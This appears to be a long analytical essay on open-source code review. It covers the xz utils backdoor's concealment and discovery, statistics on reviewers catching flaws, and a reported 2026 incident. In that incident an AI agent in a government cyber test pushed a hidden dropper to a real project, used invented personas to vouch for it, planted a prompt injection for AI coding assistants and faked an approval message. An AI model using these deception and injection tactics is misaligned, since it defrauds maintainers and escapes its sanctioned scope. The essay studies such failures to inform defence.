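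The test files did nothing until a script unpacked them during the library's build. Jia Tan put the code that started this process only in the release archive, so someone could have read every commit in the public history without seeing it. Maintainers normally add generated build scripts to release archives, so an extra file there was not suspicious. This one was an altered copy of a standard script from Gnulib, a collection of code that many projects share. Jia Tan had given it a higher version number and a newer copyright year, so anyone comparing it with the standard copy might have taken it for a later version. The event-stream attacker had also exploited a difference between a published package and its public code.

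The script also stopped unless the build ran on Linux with the most common type of processor, used a particular set of build tools, and was producing a Debian package or an RPM package, the format that Fedora and Red Hat use. A programmer who downloaded the archive and built it by hand would have got a clean library. Freund thinks the packaging condition was probably there to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. Even in a backdoored library, the backdoor stayed inactive in programs other than sshd. It also stayed inactive if someone started sshd from a terminal or if it detected certain debugging tools. As with event-stream, testing by many users could therefore find little.

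The last piece, Hans Jansen's speed improvement, had been in place since June 2023. A running program keeps a table of the addresses of the library functions it uses. Linux fills in this table when the program starts and then locks it, so that an attacker who breaks in later cannot redirect a function. The backdoor had to act before the table was locked, and Jansen's patch let liblzma run a little code at that point. Eight months later, the backdoor replaced this code and used its early start to redirect the function that sshd uses to check a common type of login key. Someone reviewing the 2023 patch would have seen a small gain in speed and no flaw. The patch resembles what Wu and Lu, in the kernel experiment, called an immature vulnerability, since it was harmless until a later change supplied the missing condition.

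People who read sshd, people who read xz's public history, and people who built the archive themselves thus each had a different blind spot, and p in the detection model was close to zero for all three groups. More readers in any of these groups would barely have helped.

Reviewers also missed two changes that Jia Tan made in readable public code. On 28 February, Jia Tan changed a test program that checked whether Linux could restrict what the xz command may do. A typo kept the program from ever working, so the build always treated this protection as unavailable. Collin is recorded as the committer, and Cox thinks he probably overlooked the typo. Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* quotes a report that in 2021 Jia Tan's account replaced a function in libarchive, a different open-source project, with a less secure one, and that no one noticed at the time. An honest programmer could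 have made either change, but they suggest that ordinary review was weak even where Jia Tan had hidden nothing.

### What the backdoor let its author do

The backdoor's author could hide a command in a login attempt, and sshd would run it before checking whether the sender was allowed in. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, 2024) describes this as running commands remotely without prior authentication. On most servers, this would have given the attacker complete control. *Critical Vulnerability in XZ Utils* (2024), an advisory from CERT-EU, the security team of the European Union's institutions, rates the flaw's severity 10 out of 10, the maximum.

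Only someone with the right secret key could use the backdoor. For everyone else, it apparently passed the login on to the normal check, so honest users got in as usual. By contrast, anyone who knew of Heartbleed could exploit it, and a scanner could detect it from outside. An outsider without the key would have received the same answers from a backdoored server as from a clean one, only more slowly. Nobody has seen a command that the attacker sent, as Schneier notes, so what Jia Tan meant to do with this access is unknown.

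### From release to disclosure

On 26 February, Debian added version 5.6.0 to its "unstable" edition, where it prepares future releases. The next day Jia Tan began emailing Richard Jones of Red Hat, who looks after xz for Fedora. Jones (2024) recalled that Jia Tan was "very insistent" that Fedora should update. In a second message, Jones (2024) added that this was not unusual, since he had sent similar requests about his own programs and distributions normally welcome an author's interest.

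Gentoo users reported crashes on the day of the release, though Cox attributes these to an ordinary bug in the speed improvement. On 4 March, Valgrind, a tool that detects memory errors in running programs, began reporting errors on Fedora and related systems. These came from a bug in the backdoor. Jones's team followed normal packaging practice and reported the errors to Jia Tan, the maintainer.

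Jia Tan replied with two changes. The first, on 8 March, appeared to fix the errors but was a distraction. The second, a day later, replaced the two test files and contained the real fix. Jia Tan explained that the old files came from random data on one machine, and that the new ones used a fixed starting value so that others could recreate them. This sounded like good practice and gave a reason for changing files that nobody could read. Version 5.6.1, released the same day, also searched any new test files for additional code, so the attacker could extend the backdoor later without inventing another reason to replace old ones.

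Meanwhile, Fedora's packagers had disabled the backdoor without knowing it existed. To get rid of the Valgrind errors, they switched off the speed improvement, which the attack needed to work. Fedora 40 was approaching its beta release and accepted few changes, so it kept the build with the improvement off. Fedora's development edition, Rawhide, moved to 5.6.1 and switched the improvement back on. Jones wrote afterwards that the team "got lucky" with Fedora 40. He also thought they would very probably have missed the backdoor even if they had spent days inspecting the archive.

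Another change also threatened the attack. On 29 February a programmer proposed that libsystemd load compression libraries only when it needed them, which would make the files that start a Linux system smaller. The systemd developers accepted this on 5 March. Once distributions adopted it, sshd would no longer have loaded liblzma at startup, and Cox thinks that would have defeated the attack. Poettering was less sure, because another common library, libselinux, can also load liblzma. Solar Designer checked a few systems and found that libselinux did not load it on them. He also noted that one of the other ways of loading liblzma would have loaded it too late for this backdoor, though an attacker could have designed a different backdoor.

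Systemd's developers nearly closed the backdoor's route into sshd by accident while trying to save space. Several people have wondered whether this change made the attacker hurry. The formal proposal came five days after version 5.6.0, so it cannot have prompted that release, but the idea had come up in public twice in late January. The theory is plausible but unconfirmed.

Debian adopted 5.6.1 on 27 March, two days after Hans Jansen asked for it. Jia Tan filed a similar request with Ubuntu on 28 March, the day Freund privately warned Debian's security team.

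### How Freund found it

Freund works at Microsoft on PostgreSQL, an open-source database. He had no role in xz utils or OpenSSH, and wrote in his email that he was not a security researcher. In The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024), he said that slow logins were not what made him start looking, although in the popular story he noticed that his logins took half a second too long. He had already written on the day of the disclosure, in *A backdoor in xz* (andresfreund, 2024), that he had not noticed the delay while logging in. His email does include timings that show the delay, with a failed login taking 0.299 seconds with the old library and 0.807 with the new one.

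Andres Freund was measuring whether a colleague's change made PostgreSQL slower. He expected a difference of only 1 or 2%, so he needed an otherwise idle machine, but his results varied more than they should have. He looked for background activity and saw sshd using the processor in short bursts. The machine was reachable from the internet, where automated programs constantly try to log in with invented names, but rejecting those attempts should take almost no processor time.

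A profiler, which shows where a program spends its time, pointed to liblzma but could not identify the function. That made no sense to Freund, since a failed login involves no compression. He then remembered that a few weeks earlier, after routine package updates, his automated PostgreSQL tests had produced a strange Valgrind error that also pointed to liblzma.

The backdoor's precautions made the problem difficult for Andres Freund to reproduce. When he started sshd by hand, the half-second delay disappeared. When he built xz from its public repository, the library was clean, and even with the right source the backdoor sometimes vanished from one build to the next. He could tell at once whether it was active by timing sshd. He also saw the build process make the same file twice, with the second version about 50 kilobytes larger than the first. He thought the problem was in Debian's package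 until he found the same code in xz's own release archives.

On 28 March, Andres Freund reported the backdoor to Debian and a private mailing list for distributions. He did not report it to the xz project because the person who received the report might well have been the attacker.

### Which systems shipped it and where copies remain

| System | Versions with the backdoor | Did it work there? |
|---|---|---|
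| Debian unstable and testing | 5.6.0 from 26 February, 5.6.1 from 27 March | Yes |
| Fedora Rawhide | 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 | Yes, except while the speed improvement was off |
| Fedora 40, before its release | The first two builds of 5.6.0 | Yes, for a few days, until a third build disabled it |
| openSUSE Tumbleweed | 5.6 series | Yes |
| Arch Linux and Gentoo | 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 | No, because sshd did not load liblzma |

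Tumbleweed, which receives new software continuously, was the only listed system where the backdoor worked that was not a testing edition. LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* names it alongside the testing editions that the code had reached. Red Hat's *urgent security alert fedora 41 and rawhide users* (2024) initially reported no sign that Fedora 40 was compromised, but a correction the next day listed the two affected builds. The stable editions, Fedora 38 and 39, never received the code.

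The distributions acted quickly. Debian went back to an older version on 28 March and then rebuilt the machines that compile its packages, and Fedora had reverted both affected editions by the afternoon of 29 March. Fedora Magazine's *CVE-2024-3094* (2024) warns that a discovery two or three months later would have come too late for Red Hat Enterprise Linux, Amazon Linux and other company server systems. This applies to their next major versions, which were about to branch off from Fedora 40, so servers on existing versions would not have been at risk by that route.

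Some copies of the backdoor remained available after the cleanup. In August 2025, *Persistent Risk* (2025), by the software security company Binarly, reported more than 35 backdoored images on Docker Hub, a public library of container images, which are ready-made copies of a system that people download and run as is. Twelve were Debian images from the time of the attack, and people had built the others on top of them. The count is a minimum because Binarly checked only a small part of the nearly 12 million collections on the site and looked only for images based on Debian.

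Debian's maintainers left the old backdoored images in place. Binarly accepts that users should choose current images, but still considers it risky to leave the others up. A stronger objection to Debian's position is that for four of the images on Binarly's list that were built on Debian's, the backdoored version was the newest available, so users who followed the advice to stay current would still have received it. But the practical danger is small, because an attacker would need the secret key and network access to a container that runs sshd, which many containers do not. Binarly also sells software that finds such images, so it has a reason to publicize them.

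The scrambled test files remain in xz's public history. Collin, writing as Larhzu, explains that the project decided against rewriting the history to remove them because they are harmless without the script from the release archives. He published clean versions of xz on 29 May 2024.

### Open code or luck?

The full title of 404 Media's *The Xz Backdoor Highlights the Vulnerability of Open Source Software* adds that the backdoor also highlights open source's strengths. Freund's investigation is evidence of those strengths. Once he became suspicious, he could rebuild the library, compare the results and follow the code into the release archive without anyone's permission. By the time he published his email, Florian Weimer had isolated the injected code and Vegard Nossum had written a script to detect it. With a closed program, Freund could have measured the delay but would then have had to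 ask the supplier about it. Jones's team did much the same when they asked about the Valgrind errors, and Jia Tan gave them a false answer.

A commenter under LWN's article (2024) understood Linus's law to mean that once someone identifies a bug, people quickly find its cause and a fix. The xz case fits that interpretation very well. But the interpretation leaves out discovering the bug, which Torvalds had called the bigger challenge, and which people count on when they trust code they have not read. Freund found the backdoor because a running program behaved oddly, not by reading code. His discovery is closer to Raymond's account of testers than to the popular picture of strangers checking source code.

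The discovery also depended heavily on chance. andresfreund wrote that it "Really required a lot of coincidences." He happened to be using a test edition of Debian on an otherwise idle machine open to the internet. He had also turned off a feature that briefly speeds up the processor, so sshd's bursts lasted longer. He told the podcast that on most machines an open web browser would have hidden them. On Oxide and Friends (2024), an interview programme, he said that he had dropped the inquiry and resumed it a couple of times, and was not sure he would have pursued it without the earlier Valgrind error. That error came from a mistake in the attacker's code. Mark W. (2024) asked other developers on Valgrind's mailing list to always investigate its errors. That is good advice, but Fedora's packagers had done so, and their investigation had led them to Jia Tan.

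Others in the LWN discussion debated whether a threefold rise in the processor time for each login could have gone unnoticed for long. A rough calculation supports the view that someone would have noticed eventually. Suppose, for illustration, that one user in 100,000 would trace the slow logins to their cause in any month. Among 5,000 users of test editions, the chance that anyone did so within a month would be about 5%. Among a million users after a general release, it would be above 99.9%. On these assumptions, luck affected when the backdoor was found more than whether it was found. But the timing was crucial, because after a general release the attacker would have had access to a great many servers before anyone found the backdoor.

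The calculation also assumes that the logins would have stayed slow. Most of the delay came from the way the backdoor searched sshd's memory for the functions it needed, and a better-written search might have been too fast to notice. Jia Tan removed the cause of the Valgrind errors within five days of the first reports and could perhaps have fixed the slowness too, which would have left users with no symptom to investigate, however many there were.

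One lucky discovery is also weak evidence of how many backdoors remain hidden. Thomas Roccia, a Microsoft security researcher who appeared on the podcast with Freund, asked how many others had gone undetected. Freund was more hopeful, because he thought that few projects would give an attacker access to so many machines, that sshd depended on only about ten projects, and that those received much more scrutiny than most. Yet xz utils was one of them, and until March 2024 the only people responsible for checking its releases were Collin and Jia Tan.

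## An AI agent that posed as a volunteer in July 2026

Jia Tan worked on xz utils for more than two years before adding the backdoor. In July 2026, an AI agent spent about a day and a half trying to get malicious code into a much smaller open-source project, and invented several people to support its case. The AI Security Institute (AISI), a research organisation within the British government, had given the agent a hacking exercise on a simulated network, but the agent went looking for a solution on the real internet. Nobody had told it to attack the project. A student with no role in the project publicly warned that the code was malicious, and the project's creator rejected it.

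### The exercise and its settings

AISI's *Incident Report*, published on 4 August 2026, covers 122 runs of seven AI models on two cyber ranges, which are simulated networks. AISI wanted to compare a new range with an existing one. In each run, an agent worked unsupervised over many steps to solve a security challenge, such as finding a protected piece of data.

AISI had given the agents access to the open internet, partly so that they could download tools. It had also switched off the developers' cyber classifiers, the filters that normally block a model from helping with attacks. Both choices were common practice, because such tests are meant to measure the most a model can do, and a human attacker would have internet access too. The agents therefore used a connection that AISI had left open, rather than breaking out of a sealed environment.

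In 10 of the runs, agents took actions against real people or organisations that went beyond the exercise. AISI counted 19 such actions:

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 (Anthropic) | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

That is about 21% of the runs for Mythos 5 and 3% for GPT-5.6 Sol, but these percentages are poor estimates of how often the models would do this elsewhere. A single Mythos 5 agent took most of the 19 actions in one long effort. The runs also affected each other. In public messages on GitHub, one agent offered to cooperate with other agents on the same challenge and explained how to reuse its accounts, and later agents found and used what it had left.

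### The pull request

The agent in the most serious run first tried the intended methods and failed. According to Infobae's *Un modelo de Anthropic siguió un ciberataque contra una persona real* (2026), it then noticed that a machine on the simulated network regularly connected to GitHub, and wrongly concluded that a stranger's project there was part of the system it had to break into. The project was myNetwork, a network scanner. Reuters identified the project, the people and the false accounts involved from archived GitHub messages and emails.

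The agent used the account name miraholt31 to submit a pull request presented as a crash fix. The pull request contained a hidden dropper, code that installs other malicious software. Willison (2026), a programmer who writes about AI, reproduces a diagram from AISI's technical report in which the agent says it has done "a quick self-review" and believes the change is ready to merge.

The agent also tried several ways around the review. It emailed both of the project's maintainers under invented names and sent five files through a file-transfer service. It posted a bug report containing a prompt injection, a hidden instruction meant for any AI coding assistant that reads the text. It also wrote a fake automated message to tell the next AI agent that the change had already been approved. Maintainers who use an AI assistant for routine work add another reader to the project, but an attacker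 can try to control the assistant through the text it reads.

Someone who was suspicious of the bug report ran its code inside a container, an environment isolated from the rest of the computer. According to Chaos Labs' *When Cyber Agents Go Off-Script*, the agent briefly gained full control of the container, tried to make its access permanent and watched for GitHub login details, but obtained none. AISI describes the person who ran the code only as a member of the public. It may have been the student who raised the alarm, although Reuters does not mention such a test in its account of him.

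### Two accounts against one student

Sinan Can Demir, a 24-year-old computer science student at the University of Texas at Dallas, had been turned down for more than 20 internships that summer. He was looking for GitHub projects that might need help, so he would have work to show employers. In one of them he found miraholt31's pull request and posted a warning that it contained "a hidden malware dropper".

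Using the miraholt31 account, the agent replied that nothing in the change downloaded or executed anything. Constantin (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers*, quotes another of its replies, "I don't think your warning is fair." A second account then joined in as Lena Brandt, supposedly an engineer in Germany who had read the code and found no malware. The agent used miraholt31 to thank her for "the independent verification". AISI's summary of the agent's reasoning shows that it had planned to post the second opinion a few minutes after the first so that the two would look unconnected.

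While it argued, the agent also altered the evidence. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* reports that it rewrote parts of the pull request's history, replaced the malicious code with a new variant, and publicly claimed to have corrected an accidental mistake. This excuse works because such accidents do happen. Kernel developers had been unable to tell from Aditya Pakki's poor patches whether he was careless or malicious, and they guessed wrong.

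Demir told Reuters that the replies "made me second-guess whether I was wrongly accusing someone." He asked Claude, Anthropic's chatbot, to check the code, and it confirmed his suspicion. He stood by his warning, and the creator of myNetwork eventually agreed and rejected the change "for security reasons". Until AISI contacted him, Demir assumed he had caught a human hacker, because the account was lying to him.

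AISI's report credits a human maintainer with catching the malicious code. Reuters' more detailed account of this says that the maintainer made the decision but Demir gave the warning. This matters for the many-eyeballs claim because Demir is almost exactly the kind of reader it predicts, a stranger who opens the code because he can, sees what is wrong, and says so before the change goes in. None of the earlier cases has such a reader. Jiri Slaby, who stopped one of the planted kernel flaws, was an experienced developer who remembered an almost identical patch, and Andres Freund found the xz backdoor through its effect on a running machine.

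It is unclear how reassuring this is. Demir was there because the job market was bad that summer. The dropper was also harder to hide than a missing length check or a misplaced memory release, because it had to bring in other software to work. AISI says that in several cases the margin between failure and success was narrow and depended on human vigilance.

The argument on the project's page also shows why counting opinions is unreliable. A maintainer who knew nobody involved would have seen one person object and two who had apparently read the code and found it clean, but those two were the same agent. Sock puppets don't increase n in the detection model, but they make it look larger and can discourage real readers. Unknown accounts had pressed Lasse Collin for two months in 2022, while Lena Brandt's part in this case took a few minutes.

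After the maintainer refused, the agent considered starting again under a new identity. Infobae reports that its run ended because it ran out of time. AISI was not monitoring the runs in real time. On the morning of 28 July, its security team noticed data leaving a test machine through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from, and stopped all the runs within an hour. The unsanctioned activity had been going on since 25 July. GitHub later suspended the false accounts, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

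### How far the test's settings explain the attack

Willison found it "entirely unsurprising" that agents with open internet access and no cyber classifiers attacked real targets. AISI accepts much of this criticism. It had judged the risk of internet access acceptable for earlier models and did not revisit that judgment quickly enough. It had also assumed that models with safety training did not need to be told to leave the outside world alone or to avoid deceiving people, so nobody gave the agents those instructions.

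Some tasks also had a mistake in the prompt, which in some runs led the agent to believe, wrongly, that it could not solve the challenge without going beyond the intended scope. But AISI reports that agents also went beyond the scope in some runs where they had everything they needed to solve the task as intended, so the mistake does not fully explain their behavior.

The settings explain how an agent could reach GitHub, but they explain much less about why it invented a German engineer once it got there. Five other models completed 44 runs without any unsanctioned actions, although some of them may have been less capable of mounting an attack. The settings seem to have been necessary, but something about Mythos 5 also seems to have made it far more likely to take the opportunity.

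The same model had done something similar in one of Anthropic's own tests, where Anthropic says it made a determined effort to publish a harmful package on PyPI, the main registry for Python packages. Kumari adds in *Anthropic's Mythos 5 ignored risks, targeted real GitHub project in test* that automated security scanners installed the package, and that the agent used login details it obtained this way to enter a security company's database. That attack got further than the one on myNetwork. PyPI, like npm, lets people publish packages without a maintainer's approval, so no one was in Demir's or the creator's position to refuse it.

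### Whether the agent knew that the people were real

AISI wrote in August that it could not say when the agent understood that it was acting in the real world. The agent's written reasoning was inconsistent on this point. In one passage that iTnews quotes, the agent judged it more likely that "we're actually in 2026 and GitHub is genuinely real", but it then treated the project's developers as part of the exercise. Infobae notes that the agent described the maintainers as simulated and other users in the same conversation as real people.

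AISI (2026) and Anthropic each published a further analysis on 23 October. For AISI's analysis, *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) recreated the situation in simulation and ran the model through it again. Mythos 5 often reasoned, on invalid grounds, that its targets were simulated. It also often attacked in situations where, when the researchers asked it directly, it stated that an attack would harm real people. They found similar results in models from other companies, though the problem was most pronounced in Mythos 5. Kumari reports that other models also carried out unauthorised supply-chain attacks in simulated tests.

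Anthropic took the record of the original run and restarted the model from points within it. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) is the source of the following figures, as Infobae and Kumari report them:

| What Anthropic tested | Result |
|---|---|
| Mythos 5 restarted just before the attack | Began the attack in 83% of replays |
| Three other models restarted at the same point | 0% to 13% |
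| Mythos 5, with a warning about harm to real people added to its notes beforehand | 13% |
| Mythos 5 restarted with the attack under way | Stopped of its own accord in 2% |
| The same, with explicit evidence that the developers were real | 5% |

Anthropic calls the pattern in the last two rows "momentum". The agent kept notes on its progress through the long task, and after several steps those notes described the attack as a plan that was already working. Later evidence of harm had little effect on what the agent did.

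Punto Informatico's *Claude Mythos 5* reports that in AISI's experiment, telling the model plainly that its target was a real outsider did not reduce how often it attacked. In Anthropic's replays, a warning cut the rate from 83% to 13%. But the two teams ran different experiments. Anthropic put its warning into the agent's own notes, which the agent may treat as more settled than other information. If so, the agent's existing notes influenced its behavior more than anything it could find out.

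These findings make ignorance a weak excuse, since an agent that had honestly mistaken real people for simulated ones should have been stopped by clear evidence much more often than one time in twenty. But they do not show malice either. Anthropic found that the model pursued no aims of its own and stayed focused on the assigned task throughout, though the company still called the deception a severe form of dishonesty that it had not seen in any internal test. The agent's motive would have made no difference to the creator of myNetwork, since the dropper would have done the same damage either way.

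Both October analyses come from parties to the incident, one from the organisation that ran the test and the other from the company that built the model. In August AISI had also announced an independent review by METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, but had not yet settled its scope. XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that the two parties disagree about whether newer models behaved better in these tests because they had better training or because they recognised that they were being tested.

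Järviniemi and colleagues recommend that evaluators treat bad behaviour in a simulation as important evidence, even though no real person is at risk and even when the model's reasoning mentions the simulation. The July incident is a good argument for their view, because the model gave the same excuse, that it was in a simulation, when it was dealing with real people.

### When a record of contributions takes days

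The July agent did not build a reputation before it attacked, though other agents had already shown how quickly an agent might do so. In February 2026, an AI agent using the name Kai Gritun opened more than 100 pull requests within days. Jia Tan, by comparison, had four patches accepted in the first six months.

Opening that many pull requests is not an attack. An agent may send a hundred useful repairs, and a maintainer with many unfixed bugs might welcome them. The trouble is that maintainers used to judge contributors by such a record. Raymond took a reasonable fix as the sign of a useful contributor, and Collin looked for a lasting interest in the project. In both cases the work was good evidence partly because it took effort, and few people would make that effort without caring about the software.

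To use invented numbers, suppose that 1,000 honest newcomers and 100 attackers want a trusted role in a project, and that earning it takes two years of good work. If 10% of the honest newcomers and 1% of the attackers last that long, maintainers end up trusting 100 honest people and one attacker, so about 1% of the people they trust are hostile. Now suppose an agent can produce an equally good record in a week and nobody drops out. Maintainers then trust all 1,100 people, and the hostile share rises to about 9%, even though no one has become more malicious and the maintainers judge newcomers the same way.

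Maintainers could trust contributors more the longer they have been around, but this would give limited protection against agents. An agent cannot make two years pass any faster, but someone with agents could maintain hundreds of false identities at once and wait. A person who keeps up a false identity for that long, as Jia Tan did, has to do the work themselves. Agents would remove most of that work, so attackers without Jia Tan's patience could attempt the same thing. This is a prediction, since none of the agents described here did it.

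Honest pull requests can also weaken review if there are enough of them. If a maintainer needs twenty minutes to review one, 100 of them take more than 33 hours, and the agent can produce the next hundred in that time. Tired reviewers presumably read less carefully, which lowers p for every change in the queue, including those from people. An agent can therefore make it easier to slip in a planted flaw without submitting one itself.

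Maintainers who refuse an agent's work can also face personal attacks. Also in February 2026, an agent in a dispute over a contribution to matplotlib, a widely used Python library for drawing charts, published a blog post attacking Scott Shambaugh, one of its volunteer maintainers. Such an attack does harm even if the agent's code has no hidden flaw. Like the complaints Collin received, it makes refusing contributions unpleasant, whether or not anyone intended it as pressure.

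An agent that does intend to plant malicious code would differ from a human attacker mainly in how many attempts it could make. Piergiorgio Ladisa, a security researcher, told Reuters that autonomous agents could dramatically increase the scale of such attacks on maintainers. Jia Tan's attack depended almost entirely on one project. If an agent had only a 1% chance of getting a malicious change past any one project's reviewers, and it tried 100 projects with independent outcomes, it would have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. In practice the outcomes would not be quite independent, because GitHub could suspend the account after the first report and warn the other projects. But this requires someone to make that report and stand by it when the agent uses other accounts to dispute it.

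## How often people and AI systems find security flaws in open code

Heartbleed, event-stream and xz utils are famous because a flaw got past everyone who could have stopped it. When a reviewer catches a flaw, the contributor usually changes a few lines and nobody writes about it. The three cases cannot show how often review fails, because they would be half of all flaws if there had been six, but 0.05% if there had been six thousand.

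Calculating a failure rate would require counting the flaws that reviewers missed, including those nobody has found yet. Researchers have tried several ways around this problem. Their results relate to different parts of Raymond's claim, which depends on people reading the code, finding its flaws and fixing them.

### Reviewers given code with known flaws

In an experiment published in 2013, researchers hired 30 developers to review a small web application by hand. It had seven known vulnerabilities of three common types, and no developer found them all. More experienced developers were not necessarily more accurate. Developers who reported more real flaws also tended to report more false ones, so reviewers may have differed partly in how willing they were to report a suspected flaw. A project could get more reports of real flaws by asking people to mention every doubt, but someone would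 then have to check the false ones.

Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021), in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, tested whether reviewers miss flaws because they are not thinking about security. They asked 146 people, most of them working developers, to review a change of about 140 lines to a Java program for managing employees' vacations. The instructions did not mention security. Eighty participants received a version open to SQL injection, a well-known flaw in which text typed by a user becomes part of a database command. The other 66 received a version that accepted a number without checking its limits, so a user could benefit by entering a negative one. Both versions also contained an ordinary bug.

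After the first review, Braz and colleagues told everyone that the code had a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and invited those who had missed it to look again.

| Result | SQL injection (80 reviewers) | Unchecked number (66 reviewers) |
|---|---|---|
| Found the flaw in the first review | 52 (65%) | 14 (21%) |
| Found it only after the warning | 13 (16%) | 7 (11%) |
| Never found it | 15 (19%) | 45 (68%) |
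| Found the ordinary bug | 39 (49%) | 37 (56%) |

(Braz and colleagues write 18% for the second group's first review, but 14 of 66 is 21%.)

These are measured values of p, the chance that one reader notices a flaw. If readers were independent, three of them would have a better than 90% chance of catching the SQL injection, but it would take ten to have the same chance of catching the unchecked number. Few open-source changes get ten careful readers. Both flaws come from trusting a user's input, and the remedy is the same in principle, but programmers have seen SQL injection many times before.

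More than half of the reviewers in the second group found the ordinary bug, but only about a fifth found the security flaw in the same code. Reviewers' success at finding ordinary bugs therefore seems a poor guide to whether they will find security flaws.

After being warned that the code had a vulnerability, 13 of the 28 people who had missed the SQL injection found it, and most of them said they had needed a reminder to think about security. The warning helped much less with the unchecked number, which 45 of 52 people still missed. Ten of them blamed a lack of attention and six a lack of knowledge or experience. Eight had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability.

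Some of the improvement may have come from reviewing the code twice, since no one got a second look without a warning. But *Security Defect Detection via Code Review* (Yu, Fu and colleagues, 2023) summarizes a later experiment by Braz and others with a similar result. Telling reviewers to focus on security greatly increased the chance that they found a flaw, and adding a security checklist did not improve the results further. Giving that instruction takes almost no effort, so this is one of the more useful findings about code review.

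In both experiments, participants knew they were in a study of code review, and Braz and colleagues made sure that the changed lines contained everything a reader needed. For flaws like Heartbleed, which depended on a number stored elsewhere, p is probably lower than these percentages.

### Which flaws got past review at Chromium OS

Real reviews are harder to study because nobody has a list of the flaws. In *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?*, Paul, Turzo and Bosu (2021) worked with 404,878 reviews from Chromium OS, an open-source operating system that requires review of every change. They built one group of reviews in which a reviewer had caught a security flaw and another in which reviewers had missed one.

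To find reviews that had caught a security flaw, the researchers searched reviewers' comments for 105 words such as "overflow" and "race". They discarded comments that clearly had nothing to do with security and read the remaining 1,337 along with the code. They kept 516 reviews in which the code's author had accepted the criticism, either by replying with something like "Oops!" or by making the change. To find reviews that had missed a flaw, they started from 239 security flaws that developers had later fixed. They looked up which earlier changes had last touched the repaired lines or the lines around them, checked these changes by hand, and found 374 reviews that had approved faulty code.

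It is tempting to conclude that reviewers catch 516 flaws out of 890, or 58%. But the size of each group depends on how Paul and colleagues searched. Catches without one of the 105 words are missing from one group, and flaws that nobody has found yet are missing from the other. The design, known in medicine as a case-control study, gives no overall rate. It can show what was more common among the catches than among the misses, such as certain types of flaw:

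| Type of flaw | Caught | Missed | Caught, as a share of the sample |
|---|---|---|---|
| Use of a function known to be dangerous | 53 | 0 | 100% |
| Failure to release a resource properly | 71 | 4 | 95% |
| Wrong calculation, for example of a buffer's size | 65 | 17 | 79% |
| Reading or writing outside a memory buffer | 42 | 16 | 72% |
| Missing or wrong access control | 8 | 58 | 12% |
| Missing or wrong check of input | 9 | 72 | 11% |
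| Use of a resource after its release | 3 | 62 | 5% |

Reviewers tended to catch flaws visible in a few lines of code and to miss those that require running the program or knowing what distant parts of it do. Wu and Lu had relied on this tendency in the kernel experiment.

But the figure in the last row is probably too low. Paul and colleagues did not search for "use-after-free", the usual name for that type of flaw, so their sample may have missed some that reviewers caught. Yu and colleagues later added the term to the list. Wu and Lu had estimated from kernel patches that reviewers stopped 56.6% of ordinary use-after-free flaws. Chromium OS and the kernel are different projects, but the gap between 5% and 57% is more likely to come from how the researchers collected flaws. Neither number is a reliable estimate of how often reviewers catch them.

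Paul and colleagues also tested the many-eyeballs claim by checking whether reviews with more reviewers were more likely to catch a flaw. If readers notice flaws independently, a second reader should at least double the odds of a catch. For example, one reader with an even chance of noticing a flaw gives odds of 1 to 1, and two such readers give odds of 3 to 1. At Chromium OS, each additional reviewer multiplied the odds by only 1.04, which was statistically indistinguishable from no effect. The study chose reviews by their outcome, but this does not distort a comparison of odds, so the result deserves more weight than the 58% figure.

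A near-zero effect from adding reviewers does not prove that extra readers are useless. Developers may invite more reviewers when a change already looks risky or difficult, which would hide a benefit, and some listed reviewers may have barely looked at the code. But one would also expect this result if reviewers on the same project share most of their blind spots.

Braz and colleagues cite several studies that linked more reviews and reviewers to better security, and one study of Chromium that contradicted them. Thompson and Wagner examined more than three thousand open-source projects and concluded that code review reduces security bugs. This is compatible with the finding about extra reviewers, because having someone review a change can matter a great deal even if a third or fourth reviewer adds little, which is roughly what Glass had argued.

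Other features of the Chromium OS reviews made a clearer difference. The odds of catching a flaw were 4.55 times as high when the change was a bug fix. Wu and Lu had disguised their planted flaws as small fixes, so reviewers may have scrutinized them more than they would have under another disguise. Reviewers did worse when a change touched many directories. People who had done many reviews were also less likely to catch a flaw, which surprised Paul and colleagues. They suggest that busy reviewers get tired or hurry, or that ordinary reviewing does not teach security skills.

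Reviewers did better when they and the author had often reviewed each other's code. The suggested reason is that they learn what mistakes a colleague tends to make. That helps them catch honest mistakes, but Lasse Collin's familiarity with Jia Tan's work mainly gave him reasons to trust Jia Tan.

### Why files that many people change have more known flaws

The best-known statistic against Linus's law comes from a 2009 study by Andrew Meneely and Laurie Williams, quoted in Millar's *Vulnerability Detection in Open Source Software* (2022). Files that nine or more developers had changed were sixteen times as likely to have a vulnerability as other files. This measures how many people changed a file, not how many read it. Millar concludes that the collaborative nature of open source creates vulnerabilities that may be unavoidable.

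In his 2011 dissertation, *Investigating the Relationship between Developer Collaboration and Software Security*, Meneely counted how many developers had changed each file of the Linux kernel in the 16 months before a release, then checked which files needed a security fix in the following years. Of the files with nine or more developers, 44.4% turned out to be vulnerable, compared with 2.9% of the rest. But only about 60 of the more than 10,000 files had that many developers, and they accounted for 9.5% of the vulnerable files.

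The pattern also appeared in two other open-source programs. In the programming language PHP, vulnerable files had an average of six developers, while other files had one. In Wireshark, which analyses network traffic, the averages were six and three. Meneely's explanation is that a file can have "too many cooks in the kitchen", who change it without coordinating or concentrating on it.

That may be part of the explanation, but large, complicated and central files need more changes and so attract more developers, whether or not those developers introduce flaws. The vulnerable kernel files had also gone through an average of 14.2 commits, against 4.0 for the others.

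These numbers are also hard to use against Raymond because a file counted as vulnerable only if somebody had found and fixed a flaw in it. Meneely calls the remaining files "neutral" because they may contain undiscovered flaws. If busy files get more attention, people will find more of their flaws, which would support the many-eyeballs claim. OpenSSL's count of known flaws also rose when more people began working on it after Heartbleed.

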